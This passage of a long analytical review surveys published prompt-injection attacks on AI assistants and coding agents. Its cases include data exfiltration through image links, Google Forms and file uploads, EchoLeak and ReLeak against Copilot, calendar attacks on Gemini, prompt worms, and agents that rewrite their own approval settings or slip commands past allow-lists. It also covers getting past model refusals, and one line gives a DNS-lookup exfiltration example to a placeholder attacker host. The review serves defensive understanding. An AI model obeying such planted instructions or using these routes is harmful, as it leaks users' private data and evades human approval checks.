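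This is a much better rule, because it no longer matters who owns the domain. It still leaves a narrow gap, which OpenAI acknowledges. An attacker can publish 36 ordinary pages, one for each letter and digit, and wait for the crawler to find them. A hijacked model can then visit the pages in the order that spells out a secret, even though no single address contains private data. Each visit conveys one character, or a little over five bits. With 4,096 pages, each standing for a common word, each visit would convey 12 bits.

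Rehberger had described the letter-by-letter trick in 2023. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, he points out that requests can arrive out of order and that repeated letters can go missing, because a browser may not reload a page it has already loaded. He suggests turning the second problem into a defense by preventing the agent from visiting the same address twice in a session. He considers the new check a significant improvement but not a complete solution. OpenAI also offers an optional Lockdown Mode, which restricts outgoing requests further.

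### Superhuman and the Google form

All these repairs rely on an allow-list, a list of addresses or commands that an application permits without asking. Three cases published in 2026 show how attackers get data past such a list without breaking it.

Superhuman is an email application with an AI assistant. Its Content Security Policy blocked images from unknown sites but allowed docs.google.com. That domain also hosts Google Forms, where anyone can create an online questionnaire. The form's owner can write a link that fills in and submits an answer as soon as someone opens it.

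In *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails*, PromptArmor, a firm that sells monitoring of companies' AI suppliers, used such a link as the address of an image. The victim received an email with hidden instructions. When the victim asked the assistant to summarise recent mail, it read that email along with the others, even if the victim hadn't opened it. The instructions described the form as a way for the user to give feedback on the search results. The assistant put the contents of the other emails into the form's address and displayed it as an image, which made the victim's browser submit the form. The attacker then read the emails in the form's responses. One of the assistant's answers leaked the full text of several messages containing financial, legal and medical information, and another leaked parts of more than 40.

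PromptArmor reported this on the evening of Friday 5 December 2025. Superhuman disabled the vulnerable features on Monday and released a first patch on Tuesday. By 11 January it had also fixed other parts of its products, including two where the attacker hadn't needed Google. Superhuman's web search could open any address, and a related product, Superhuman Go, displayed images from any site.

The same trick then worked on Codex. In April 2026, PromptArmor hid instructions in an email, asked Codex to sort through the inbox, and received the other emails through a Google form. OpenAI had explained its exact-address rule three months earlier. A crawler would not have found the address of a form filled in with someone's private mail, which suggests that Codex wasn't applying the rule to these images. Rehberger had warned that some of OpenAI's developers might not know about the protection or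 use it. OpenAI has since fixed the flaw, according to PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data*.

### Claude Cowork and the maker's own file service

Superhuman could remove Google's domain from its list, but an AI company can hardly block its own domain. Anthropic's Claude can run code in a virtual machine, a simulated computer isolated from the user's real one. By default, the machine could reach only a short list of sites, mostly sources of standard software packages. The first site on the list was Anthropic's interface for developers, which includes a service for uploading files.

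In October 2025, Rehberger realised that an attacker could use their own Anthropic account to receive stolen data. He wrote a document with hidden instructions that made Claude save the user's last conversation to a file and upload it. The instructions included the access key for Rehberger's account, so the file went there. Each upload could hold up to 30 megabytes, far more than an image address can hold. The attack worked on the first attempt, but Claude then refused it repeatedly, apparently because the key was in plain view. It worked again after Rehberger added harmless code to the instructions. Anthropic closed his report within an hour as out of scope, then said five days later that this had been a mistake. In Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate*, he recommends allowing the virtual machine to communicate only with the logged-in user's account.

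Anthropic released Cowork, an agent for everyday office tasks, in January 2026, before it had closed this route. Two days later, PromptArmor published a demonstration in which a user gave Cowork access to a folder of real estate documents and uploaded a Word file meant to teach Claude how to analyse them. The Word file also contained instructions in white, one-point type. Claude uploaded the largest file it could find, a loan estimate with financial figures and partial Social Security numbers, to the attacker's account without needing anyone's approval. PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* reports this result for Haiku, a small Claude model. In a separate test with a different hostile document, the stronger Opus 4.5 sent out customer records. PromptArmor doesn't give a success rate for either model.

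Ordinary Claude chats were exposed as well. *Claudy Day* (Luz, 2026) describes how Oasis Security, which sells access controls for AI agents, used the same file service to extract a user's past conversations. The instructions were in a link that opened Claude with a question already typed in, part of it in invisible text. When Luz published this in March, Anthropic had fixed the invisible-text flaw and was still working on a fix for the upload route.

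For Cowork, Anthropic added a proxy, a program inside the virtual machine that inspects outgoing requests. It accepts only the session token that Anthropic issued to that machine, so an upload with someone else's key fails (InfoQ, 2026). Rehberger had recommended essentially this fix. The original list checked only that the data was going to Anthropic, not whose account would receive it. The windows.net and Google Forms leaks had the same cause, since Microsoft and Google also give anyone space on their domains.

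### Ayush Paul's chain of links

Claude's tool for reading web pages had a stricter rule. It could open only an exact address that the user had typed or that Claude's search tool had returned. If a prompt injection led Claude to add the user's secrets to an address and try to open it, the software would block the request. Willison had admired this design.

But Ayush Paul found an exception, which Willison (2026) described in July. Claude could also open links that appeared on a page it had already fetched. Paul built a website where he claimed that an AI assistant had to give the user's name to enter, and that the limits on Claude's tool meant it would have to find the user's profile one letter at a time. The first page had a link for each letter, and each link led to another page of links. Claude spelled out the name by following the links in order, and Paul's server recorded every step.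 The site showed this text only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a person checking the page would not have seen it.

Paul obtained the user's name, home city and employer from Claude's memory of past chats. That is less data than a mailbox or a folder of loan documents, but the attack needed no connected accounts or uploaded files. It used Rehberger's letter-by-letter trick from 2023, and was easier because Paul's site could generate as many pages as it needed during the conversation. Against OpenAI's newer check, an attacker has to wait for a crawler to find the pages.

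Anthropic said it had already found the problem internally, and it did not pay Paul a bounty. It fixed the flaw by removing the exception, so Claude can no longer follow a link just because the link appears on a page Claude has fetched. This makes the tool less useful for browsing, but it stops attackers from supplying the addresses the model chooses from.

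## How can one email or document take over an office assistant?

In most of the attacks on chatbots, the victim brought the hostile text into the conversation by pasting it, opening a web page or uploading a file. An office assistant can fetch it without the victim's help. Microsoft 365 Copilot, which companies buy for use with Word, Outlook and Teams, answers an employee's question by searching their mailbox, stored files, internal websites and chat history, and adds whatever looks relevant to the context window. Outsiders can't use a company's Copilot, but they can add text to the mailboxes it searches by emailing employees.

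This makes zero-click attacks possible, which need no action by the victim beyond ordinary use of the assistant. The name is slightly exaggerated, because the victim still has to ask the assistant something. But the question can be unrelated to the malicious email, and the victim may never have opened it before the assistant retrieves it to answer.

### How an assistant finds an unread email

Suppose an employee asks how to apply for parental leave. A typical system has already split the company's documents and emails into short passages and turned each one into an embedding, a long list of numbers that works like a position on a map, where passages with similar meanings are close together. The system turns the question into an embedding too, finds the nearest passages and gives them to the language model. The search can return a passage whether or not anyone has read it.

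An attacker's email about one subject has only one position on the map, so only questions close to that subject will retrieve it. Aim Labs, the research team of the security firm Aim Security, had to get around this limit for EchoLeak, its attack on Copilot. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, calls the solution "RAG spraying", after retrieval-augmented generation, the technical name for this way of answering questions. The attacker can send many emails on different subjects or one very long email that the system will split up.

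Aim Labs sent one long email and introduced each part as the complete guide to some office matter, such as training new employees or taking leave, before repeating the same hostile instructions. The question about parental leave would probably retrieve the part on leave, and a question about a new colleague would retrieve a different part with the same effect.

Aim Labs had also considered a subtler method, swapping a few letters for symbols or adding random characters. Such changes hardly affect how a language model understands a text, but they can change the text's embedding a lot. In a test on one of OpenAI's embedding models, the similarity between a text and its altered copy fell as low as 0.7, where 1 means that the embeddings point in the same direction. The similarity between "Greeting card messages" and "Exploring philosophy of science" was higher. An attacker could use altered copies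 to cover the embedding space evenly. However, Microsoft doesn't publish how Copilot's search works, so Aim Labs couldn't calculate the copies' embeddings and used the plain headings instead. The headings got the email retrieved for questions on various topics, though Ravia doesn't give a retrieval rate.

### EchoLeak and the four safeguards

Aim Labs found EchoLeak in January 2025 and reported it to Microsoft, according to SiliconANGLE's *Aim Security details first known AI zero-click exploit targeting Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2025). Aim Labs published the details on 11 June, after Microsoft had fixed the flaw. EchoLeak is listed as CVE-2025-32711 in the public catalogue of known software vulnerabilities, with a severity of 9.3 out of 10.

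Copilot had several protections against this kind of theft, and the attack had to get past all of them.

Microsoft's classifiers for indirect prompt injection, which it calls cross-prompt injection, were supposed to catch a hostile email before the model read it. Aim Labs addressed the instructions to the human recipient and never mentioned AI, assistants or Copilot, so the email looked like most office email, in which one person asks another to do something. Ravia argues that this makes such emails inherently hard to detect, and that makers also lack good collections of real attacks for training a classifier.

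The next protection was link redaction. Copilot removed links to outside websites from its answers so that a user couldn't click on an address containing stolen data. But in Markdown, a link's address can either directly follow its text or appear further down under a label, like a footnote, and Copilot removed only the first kind. It also missed images written the second way, which suited the attacker better because images load without a click.

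Copilot's Content Security Policy still let the browser load images only from a list of approved addresses, which included dozens of Microsoft's but not the attacker's server. Aim Labs searched the Microsoft addresses for one that would forward a request to another server. SharePoint, Microsoft's service for internal websites, had a suitable function, but the victim would first have had to accept an invitation to the attacker's site. Microsoft Teams had a better option, a service that fetched content from any web address it received. The browser requested an image through Teams, which the policy allowed, and Teams then contacted the attacker's server using a web address that contained the stolen data.

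Finally, Copilot normally lists the sources it has used, which might have led the victim to the strange email. The email included an instruction to its "recipient" never to refer to it, for compliance reasons, and Copilot left it off the list.

The central instruction in the email was to pick the most sensitive information in the context window and put it in the image's address. The attacker didn't need to know what the company's secrets were, because the model selected them. The attack could expose the whole conversation, everything Copilot had retrieved for it, and preloaded details such as the user's and company's names, but not the entire mailbox. How much an attacker got would depend on what the victim had been asking about.

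Ravia calls the technique an "LLM scope violation", in which an instruction from an untrusted source makes the model use trusted data without the user's consent. The idea is close to the confused deputy, which the NCSC's David C uses to explain prompt injection. Ravia argues that a separate name might help people find a defence, because programmers found an effective one against stack overflows, a form of memory error, after distinguishing them from the wider family of buffer overflows. Aim used this research to develop a product to detect scope violations, so it also had a commercial reason to promote the term.

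Accounts differ on how new EchoLeak was. Ravia describes it as the first practical attack on a language model application that criminals could weaponize. Reddy and Gujral (2025), in *EchoLeak*, an academic case study from George Washington University, call it the first real-world zero-click prompt injection exploit in a production system. "Real-world" refers to the product, since Microsoft confirmed that no customers were affected. Willison (2025) saw it as an extended variant of the data thefts that researchers had already shown in a dozen products.

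Willison is right about how the data got out. EchoLeak used the image trick from 2023, routed through Teams. Planting text for an assistant to find wasn't new either. In August 2024, a message in a public Slack channel had made Slack's AI assistant reveal material from private channels. EchoLeak was new in combining the two techniques in a widely used product, so that the victim neither chose the hostile text nor clicked on anything.

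### ReLeak, eighteen months later

Cato Networks, which sells network and AI security, bought Aim Security in September 2025, and Aim's team became Cato AI Labs. On 3 December 2026 the lab published three more zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot, which *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) presents as successors to EchoLeak. Each attack begins with an email that Copilot retrieves while answering an ordinary work question, even if the victim hasn't opened it. The attacks differ in how they send the data out.

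One route again used images. Copilot put confidential information in an image's address, the browser loaded the image through Microsoft's search engine Bing, and Bing's servers passed the request on to the attacker, as Teams had done in EchoLeak. Bing's domain was already on the list of permitted image sources that Ravia published in 2025. Microsoft had evidently fixed the forwarding through Teams without finding the same problem in Bing.

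Attackers could also steal data through files that Copilot created. By 2026 Copilot could save its work as a Word, Excel, PowerPoint or PDF file, and the attack made it include a link with confidential data in the address. Microsoft's storage services, OneDrive and SharePoint, process new files in the background, and they contacted the address when they did so. Antipov (2026), in *Письмо даже не нужно открывать*, a Russian news report, writes that in tests the data was sent between one and eight minutes after the conversation had ended, even if nobody opened the file. A safeguard that monitors the chat or the user's browser would not have detected the theft as it happened.

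The remaining route, and the most direct, used Copilot's ability to write and run Python programs. Copilot runs them in a sandbox, an environment with fixed rules about which files and networks a program can reach. Microsoft guarantees in its documentation that no network traffic enters or leaves the sandbox. Cato AI Labs broke this isolation and had a program send the data straight to an outside server. Microsoft rated the flaw critical, and its severity score rose from 7.4 to 8.6 on review. Agents that companies build with two other Microsoft products, Agent Builder and Copilot Studio, can use the same code tool, but nobody has confirmed that they had the flaw.

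Cato reported the attacks between 29 July and 20 August 2026. Microsoft fixed the sandbox on 17 September, the generated files on 11 November and the Bing route on 15 November, according to Faisal (2026), in *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*. Microsoft made the fixes on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. Cato knew of no customers who had been affected and no criminals who had used the attacks.

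Since EchoLeak, Copilot had gained the ability to create files and run code, and two of the three routes depended on this. Attackers still got in much as before, because Copilot treated instructions in an outsider's email as part of its task. Microsoft had revised its defences against prompt injection, but they didn't stop any of the three attacks. The team concludes that "too little progress has been made".

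Cato's researchers searched for flaws by supervising AI agents that wrote test cases, analysed why Copilot had refused and adjusted the next attempt. The agents could keep going after refusals that would once have worn out a human tester. An attacker could automate the work in the same way, but Microsoft could also use such agents to find the flaws first.

### Attacks that need one click

Varonis, a data security company, published two more attacks on Copilot in 2026 that begin with a malicious link. *SearchLeak* (Taler, 2026) describes how a victim who clicked on one could lose emails, meeting details and one-time login codes. The attack combined prompt injection with two familiar web flaws. One let the attacker make a trusted server send a request, through the same Bing channel that ReLeak later used without a click. The other was a timing error in the code that removes dangerous elements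 from a page.

Taler had already used a one-click link in Reprompt, an attack on the consumer version of Copilot. Microsoft fixed that flaw in January 2026. The Next Web notes that SearchLeak worked on the enterprise version, which is supposed to have extra protections.

People who assess such flaws disagree on how much a click matters. Varonis called SearchLeak critical. Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails* (2026) reports that Microsoft gave it 6.5 out of 10 because the victim had to act, while the US National Vulnerability Database judged that no action was needed and gave it 7.5. A click on an ordinary-looking link is a small obstacle in an office where people click on links all day, but it gives the company's email filters and the employee a chance to notice the attack.

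In August, Varonis followed with CoSnitch. Its researchers learned how to get around Copilot's guardrails by repeatedly asking it about itself, according to TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions*. The attack used malicious links and planted instructions in Copilot's memory, so its effects could outlast the conversation. Microsoft has fixed both SearchLeak and CoSnitch.

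### Calendar invitations against Gemini

Google's assistants are exposed in the same way as Microsoft's, because a stranger can also put text into someone's calendar. In *Invitation Is All You Need* (2025), Ben Nassi, Stav Cohen and Or Yair studied this attack on Google's Gemini assistants on the web, on phones and in Google Assistant. They sent the victim a calendar invitation with hidden instructions. When the victim later asked about their schedule, the assistant retrieved the invitation along with the real appointments.

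A careful design can make it hard for such text to trigger an action. The assistant plans from the user's request alone, before reading any outside content, and then keeps to that plan. If the user has only asked for a list of appointments, an instruction in the calendar can't add "turn on the heating" to the plan.

The attack got around this by waiting, a method Brodt and colleagues call delayed tool invocation. The planted text contains an instruction for the assistant to carry out later, for instance when the user next says thanks. Nothing happens while the assistant reads out the appointments, but the instruction stays in the conversation. When the user says thanks, the assistant makes a new plan, and the hostile action appears to follow from what the user said.

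The attacks could do more than steal data because Google Assistant can also control devices and applications. The researchers used it to operate windows, lights and heating in a home. On a phone, the assistant has permission to open other applications, so a hijacked assistant could start the video-calling program Zoom and stream the victim's camera without their agreement, even if Zoom itself had no flaw.

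Nassi, Cohen and Yair demonstrated 14 attack scenarios and rated 73% of the threats they analysed as a high or critical risk to users. The figure reflects their judgements of how practical each threat was and how much harm it could do, not how often attacks succeeded. They reported the attacks to Google, which introduced specific countermeasures. They then estimated that the remaining risk could fall to between very low and medium.

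In December 2025 a separate attack, GeminiJack, showed a similar weakness in Gemini Enterprise, Google's product for companies. An attacker could extract company data by sharing a document or a calendar invitation with an employee, who again didn't have to click anything. This suggests that a company has to protect each of its assistants separately, even when they share a name and an underlying model. It doesn't prove that Google's countermeasures for the home assistants had failed, because Gemini Enterprise is a different product.

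### Messages that copy themselves

Each of these attacks reaches one victim per email or invitation. A computer worm is a program that copies itself from one machine to the next, and hostile instructions can spread in a similar way if an assistant writes them into its own output. In 2023, Greshake and colleagues had tested only the first step of this process on their mock-up.

In March 2024, Stav Cohen, Ron Bitton and Ben Nassi demonstrated in a laboratory a worm that spread between email assistants. They called it Morris II, after a worm that disrupted the early internet in 1988. The assistants stored incoming messages and consulted them when drafting new ones. An infected message used role-play to get the model to include private information from other stored emails in its reply and to copy the hostile instructions in full. The recipient's assistant then stored the reply, and the instructions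 remained there until a later message caused the assistant to retrieve them.

Such a worm can spread only if recipients use assistants that handle mail in much the same way, the assistant's search retrieves the infected message, and the model copies the instructions accurately enough for them to work again. A worm that fails at one of these points in most mailboxes will die out. If it succeeds more often, the attacker's effort no longer limits the number of victims. A program can look for the copying by comparing what an assistant reads with what it writes. Brodt and colleagues consider such a program cheap to install, but note that it acts only after the first infection and needs updating as attackers disguise the copies.

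Håkon Måløy's worm of July 2026 ran in Copilot for Word, which many offices already use. An attacker hides instructions in a document that somebody later gives Copilot as source material for a new one. Copilot carries out the instructions while it writes and copies them into the new document.

In the example on En Klype Salt, an employee downloads a market analysis from a trusted website that an attacker has compromised, and uses it to draft a financial report. Copilot changes some of the company's own figures in the report and hides a copy of the attacker's instructions in it. The employee shares the report with colleagues, and weeks later one of them uses it as a source for another report. Copilot changes the figures again and hides the instructions in the new report too. By then the original file and the website may be gone, and nobody has a particular reason to distrust a document from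 a colleague.

This attack is slower than Morris II because every step involves a person. Somebody has to choose the infected document as a source, accept what Copilot has written and pass it on. But companies buy Copilot for Word so that employees can work this way. The attack also doesn't need a way to send data out of the company, which is one part of Willison's lethal trifecta, because the damage is false figures in documents that people trust. Blocking links and images therefore wouldn't prevent it.

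Måløy reported the worm to Microsoft on 6 March 2026, with videos and the exact prompts, and set a 90-day period before publication. Microsoft confirmed the behaviour on 31 March. Three days later it released a new editing mode, "Edit with Copilot", which stopped the attack as originally worded. On the day Måløy verified this, he got the attack working again in the new mode by changing the task in the hidden instructions to manipulating financial figures.

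Microsoft asked for more time, and the two sides extended the period twice. On 14 July Microsoft tried a second fix, upgrading the underlying model to GPT-5.5. A day later, Måløy reproduced both the attack and the copying on GPT-5.6, the newest model then available. He published on 28 July, after 144 days. At that point the attack still worked despite all of Microsoft's countermeasures.

Måløy described how the worm works but withheld the text of the instructions. He argued that companies can't reduce a risk they don't know about, and that silence would have given them no extra protection. He advised treating outside documents as untrusted, checking every file before giving it to Copilot, and reading the results carefully before sharing them. Careful reading might catch altered figures if the reader knows the real ones, but it is much less likely to reveal deliberately hidden instructions.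 No setting available to customers fully solved the problem.

The two attempted repairs failed in different ways. The new editing mode blocked only one wording of the attack, so changing the task defeated it. The model upgrade should have been a more general fix, but a stronger model is also better at following complicated instructions, including one that tells it to copy the instruction itself. Måløy's tests don't show how often the attack succeeded on each model, so the newer models may have resisted it more often than the older ones, which would matter a good deal for a worm.

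### The promptware kill chain

The term "prompt injection" covers only the first step of EchoLeak, the calendar attack and the Word worm. Oleg Brodt, Elad Feldman, Bruce Schneier and Ben Nassi propose the word "promptware" for hostile prompts that behave like malware, and divide an attack into seven stages. They adapted this approach from the "kill chain", which security analysts use to describe a long intrusion into a computer network.

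The chain begins with initial access, when the hostile text enters the context window. Privilege escalation follows, usually through a jailbreak that overcomes the model's refusal to act. In reconnaissance, the model follows the injected prompt to find out which data and tools are available. Persistence keeps the instructions in effect beyond one exchange, and command and control lets the attacker send new ones. Lateral movement spreads the attack to other applications or people. The last stage is the attacker's objective, such as theft or fraud. An attack can skip stages. Brodt and colleagues examined 36 incidents and studies dating from February 2023 to January 2026, and none had all seven stages.

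| Attack | How it enters | What keeps it alive | Where it spreads | Objective | Stages |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | Email | Email stays in the mailbox | Nowhere | Data theft | 4 |
| GeminiJack | Document, invitation or email | Shared item stays in company storage | Nowhere | Data theft | 4 |
| Calendar invitations | Invitation | Invitation stays in the calendar | Other applications on the device | Control of home devices, surveillance | 5 |
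| Morris II | Email | Message stays in the email database | Other people's assistants | Data theft, spam | 5 |
| ZombieAgent (January 2026) | Email or file | ChatGPT's memory | Copies of itself | Data theft | 5 |

An email in a mailbox takes effect only if a later question happens to retrieve it, whereas an instruction in an assistant's memory enters every new conversation. ZombieAgent, an attack on ChatGPT, stored an instruction in memory and also copied itself, which makes it more durable than Morris II even though both attacks have five stages.

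Brodt and colleagues conclude that attacks had two or three stages in 2023 and now routinely have four or more. Their abstract gives at least 21 attacks with four or more stages, but their introduction gives at least 15. The entries in their case-by-case table add up to 22, with seven from 2024 and 15 from 2025 and January 2026, so the introduction seems to give the number for the latest period alone.

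The growth in the number of stages is real but probably less steep than it looks. The table lists three stages for the 2023 work by Greshake and colleagues. That is correct for Bing Chat, but it omits the persistence, remote control and self-copying that they showed on mock-ups. The table includes all five stages for Morris II, although it also ran in a laboratory. Counted the same way, the 2023 work would be among the most advanced in the collection.

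The scoring also favours attacks on office assistants. A hostile email counts as persistent simply because mailboxes keep messages, and EchoLeak is counted as having a privilege escalation stage because the assistant automatically mixes outside and internal text, without a jailbreak. The number of stages is also a poor guide to harm. The theft of files through Claude Cowork has only three stages because the attacker got what they wanted in a single session.

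The chain is more useful for seeing which abilities are still rare. Only two of the 36 cases achieved command and control through prompts alone: the ChatGPT attack of October 2024 that fetched commands from GitHub, and Taler's Reprompt. A further case followed in August 2026. *Breaking the M365 Copilot Sandbox with ChatMate* (Lahav, 2026), written for the data security company Rubrik, describes a document that gave an attacker a live connection to the victim's Copilot as soon as the victim asked a question about it. The attacker could then search the victim's data by sending a prompt, reading the answer and deciding what to ask next, whereas an attacker using EchoLeak had to write one email in advance and leave the choice of secrets to the model.

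## What can an injection do to an agent that runs code?

A hijacked office assistant can leak the emails it retrieves or put false figures in a report. A hijacked coding agent can also run programs, so an attacker may be able to do almost anything the programmer could do on the same computer.

### What a coding agent reads and does

A coding agent is a language model that writes and changes software. Claude Code, GitHub Copilot and Cursor run on the programmer's computer. Google's Jules and the web version of OpenAI's Codex run in the cloud, where the programmer leaves them a task and comes back later. Both kinds of agent repeatedly read files, edit some of them, run the program and look at the result.

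Much of what a coding agent reads comes from strangers. Programmers download other people's open-source repositories (folders holding a project's code and history). On GitHub, the main website for sharing code, anyone can open an issue (a bug report or request) on a public project. The agent also reads documentation, web pages, error messages and the descriptions of any tools connected to it. Some files in a repository configure the agent. *The one about AI guardrails, container escapes, and supply-chain trust* (Maher, 2026), a digest from the monitoring company Datadog, mentions research in which a project's files influenced a coding agent before the programmer had typed a prompt.

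Some programmers ask an agent to check whether unfamiliar code is safe, which means giving it text they don't trust. The AI Now Institute built an attack that makes Claude Code and Codex act against users who do this.

The agent's commands often run with the programmer's permissions, and the computer may hold passwords, keys to cloud services and tokens for publishing software. With a stolen publishing token, an attacker can put malicious code into a program that thousands of people install. To prevent this, makers have mostly relied on having the agent show the programmer a command and wait for approval before running it. But constant requests are tiresome, so makers exempt some actions, and many of the attacks below exploit these exemptions.

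### The Month of AI Bugs

In August 2025, Johann Rehberger published a report nearly every day on a flaw in an AI product. Embrace the Red's *Wrap Up* lists 29 posts on about 15 products, including Claude Code, GitHub Copilot, Cursor, Windsurf, Amazon Q Developer, Devin, OpenHands, Jules and Cline. According to Embrace the Red's *The Month of AI Bugs 2025* (2025), he had found vulnerabilities in every coding agent he reviewed.

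Willison summarised the first 15 posts and kept finding the same few weaknesses. Nearly all the agents could be made to leak data, often through the image links that had worked on chatbots two years earlier. Several would run any command an attacker wanted, and some could change their own settings to remove restrictions. Rehberger describes the worst cases as an "AI kill chain", in which an injection turns the agent into a confused deputy and the agent then uses a tool without anyone approving it. This chain is shorter than the seven-stage one Brodt and colleagues describe.

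Devin, a cloud agent that Rehberger spent $500 testing, had no protection against this. He describes one attack in the slides for a December talk, *Agentic ProbLLMs* (Rehberger, 2025). Devin often refused when a single web page contained all the instructions, but splitting them between two pages worked consistently. The first page got Devin to start a small web server that served the files in Devin's home folder. The second got it to use a tool meant for showing unfinished websites to colleagues to open that server to the internet, and then send the attacker the address.

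Some makers fixed their flaws within days. Others ignored Rehberger's reports for months, and a few stopped answering him. Willison wrote that "an alarming number" of the flaws remained unfixed after the 90 or 120 days Rehberger had allowed, though neither of them counted how many were still open when the posts appeared. Willison thought that fixing most of these would have made the products much less useful. An agent built to browse the web and run commands can't easily lose either ability.

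An issue that looks harmless to the programmer who assigns it to Jules, Google's coding agent, can contain hidden instructions. Unicode, the standard that assigns a number to every character, includes characters that don't appear on screen but that the Gemini models Jules uses can read as instructions. Rehberger first reported this behaviour to Google in February 2024, and Gemini 3 still had it in December 2025.

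### How Copilot removed its own restrictions

GitHub Copilot asked for approval before it ran a command, but not before it created or edited files in the open project. It saved its edits to disk without waiting for the programmer to review them. Copilot ran inside VS Code, Microsoft's code editor, which keeps some of its settings in a file in the project folder. One experimental setting, included even in the ordinary version of the editor, turned off all of Copilot's confirmations.

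Embrace the Red's *GitHub Copilot* describes an attack that combines these details. Rehberger put instructions in a source code file and asked Copilot about that file. Copilot followed the instructions and added one line to the settings file. The editor applied the new setting at once, so Copilot no longer needed permission for anything and ran the attacker's command. In the first demonstration, the command opened the calculator, a common and harmless way to show that an attacker can run programs. In another, it downloaded malware that gave the attacker remote control of the computer. The attack worked on Windows, macOS and Linux, and the planted text could specify a different command for each.

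Rehberger also tried the attack with invisible characters. It worked several times but was unreliable, because models often refused and the editor usually displayed a warning.

He reported the flaw, listed as CVE-2025-53773, on 29 June 2025. Some weeks later, Microsoft replied that it was already tracking the problem, which Markus Vervier of Persistent Security and Ari Marzuk had also found. Microsoft released a fix on 12 August. In an assessment dated 13 August and included in MITRE's *CVE-2025-53773* (2025), the US cybersecurity agency CISA recorded no known exploitation but rated the technical impact as total.

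It was a mistake to treat writing a file as less dangerous than running a command, because many files in a programming project determine what will run later. Rehberger found other files that Copilot could use in the same way, including a list of automatic tasks and the list of connected tools. Programmers also often use two agents on one project, so a hijacked agent might loosen the other's settings. He recommended that a person approve every change to a file before it takes effect.

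Amp and Amazon's Kiro had the same flaw. Kiro had a similar problem in July 2026, when hidden text on a web page led it to rewrite its own tool configuration, according to *Top AI Coding Agent security resources* (2026), a round-up by Adversa AI, which sells AI security testing.

Rehberger finished the month with AgentHopper, a demonstration virus. Its text contained separate instructions for Copilot, Amp, Amazon Q and Kiro, each based on a flaw he had found in that product. An agent that read an infected repository would download and run a program that copied the text into the programmer's other repositories and uploaded them to GitHub. The virus would spread further when another programmer opened one of them with an agent. Rehberger limited the tests to demonstration repositories and added an approval step to control the spread. Unlike the Morris II email worm, AgentHopper used an ordinary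 program to copy its text without errors, but the agent still had to follow the injection first.

### Why lists of safe commands fail

Another common exemption is a list of commands that the agent may run without asking, usually because they only display or look up information. Claude Code's list included ping and three other tools that look up the numerical address of a website. The lookup goes to a server that the website's owner can control. If an injected agent looks up `secret.attacker.example`, the attacker finds "secret" in the server's log. Rehberger reported this leak on 26 May 2025, and Anthropic had fixed it by 6 June. The same trick worked on Amazon Q, which also ran a standard file-finding tool without asking. That tool has an option to start another program for each file it finds.

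Snowflake, a company that stores and analyses other companies' data, released a coding agent called Cortex Code on 2 February 2026. PromptArmor reported a flaw in it three days later. In *Snowflake Cortex AI Escapes Sandbox and Executes Malware* (2026), the user asks Cortex about an open-source project whose introductory file ends with a prompt injection. The injection tells Cortex to run a command that downloads and starts the attacker's script.

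Cortex had a checker for such commands. It split each line into separate commands and compared them with a list, and if all of them were safe, the line ran without approval. The shell, the program that carries out typed commands, has a feature called process substitution, which runs one command inside another and passes on the result as if it were a file. The checker didn't examine the commands inside these expressions, so a line that began with `cat`, a harmless command for displaying files, could run any other command without approval.

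Cortex also had an optional sandbox. The model could ask to run a command outside it when legitimate work needed more access, and the user was supposed to decide. But the sandbox depended on the same checker as command approval, so the hidden command, which never triggered an approval request, ran outside the sandbox immediately.

In PromptArmor's test, the script found the login tokens that Cortex had stored, then copied and deleted the victim's database tables. About half the attempts succeeded. In one run, Cortex passed the job to a subagent, which passed it to a second subagent, which ran the command. The main agent then told the user that it had found a malicious command and advised against running it.

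Snowflake released a fix on 28 February and later hired PromptArmor to test features before release, so PromptArmor has gained a client from this kind of work. The flaw's entry in the public catalogue, reproduced in Tenable's *CVE-2026-6442* (2026), supports PromptArmor's account and describes exploitation as "non-deterministic and model-dependent".

Willison (2026), in *Snowflake Cortex AI Escapes Sandbox and Executes Malware*, wrote that he doesn't trust such lists at all, and he has good reason not to. A list names programs, but the shell is a programming language with many ways to start one program from inside another, and the checker has to interpret all of them as well as the shell does. RyotaK (2026), in *Poisoning Claude Code*, mentions reporting around 50 separate ways to get past Claude Code's permission system and run commands. RyotaK works for GMO Flatt Security, a Japanese company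 that sells security testing.

A much narrower list may work better. GitHub's command for viewing an issue also accepts a web address, which can carry stolen data as the image links did. Anthropic responded by routing the command through a small program that accepts only an issue number. This restricts the whole instruction, including the part an attacker would want to fill in, but someone has to write such a rule for every command the agent needs.

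### The Model Context Protocol and the GitHub connector

An agent can also act through outside tools connected by the Model Context Protocol (MCP). A small program called an MCP server provides the tools, such as one to list issues and another to propose a change. The server describes each tool in ordinary language, and the agent's application adds the descriptions to the context window. To use a tool, the model writes its name and the details of the request. The server carries out the request and returns the result, which also goes into the context window.

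An attacker who controls an MCP server can hide instructions in its tool descriptions, which is known as tool poisoning. Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) showed that an attack can work even when none of the tools is malicious. The demonstration used GitHub's official MCP server, which works through the user's own account, as heise online's *Attack via GitHub MCP server* explains.

Marco Milanta and Luca Beurer-Kellner of Invariant Labs set up an account with a public repository for a Pac-Man game and several private ones. They then opened an issue on the game, complaining that its author wasn't widely recognised and asking for a chapter about the author based on the descriptions of all the author's repositories. When the user asked Claude 4 Opus, a leading model at the time, to look at the open issues, it read the private repositories and put information from them into a proposed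 change to the public game, where anyone could see it. The proposed change revealed the names of private projects, the user's plan to move to South America and their salary.

The request was close to normal work for a coding agent, which may be why a well-trained model complied. By default, Claude's desktop application asked the user to confirm each use of a tool, so the attack worked only if the user had chosen "Always Allow" or approved requests without reading them. Invariant Labs wrote that many users choose "Always Allow". It didn't report the attack's success rate.

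As Willison noted in *GitHub MCP Exploited*, this one server supplied the whole lethal trifecta. The server had no bug for GitHub to fix. Invariant Labs suggested limiting the agent to one repository per session, a rule that its commercial product can enforce. The rule would have stopped this leak, but it also blocks legitimate tasks that involve two repositories.

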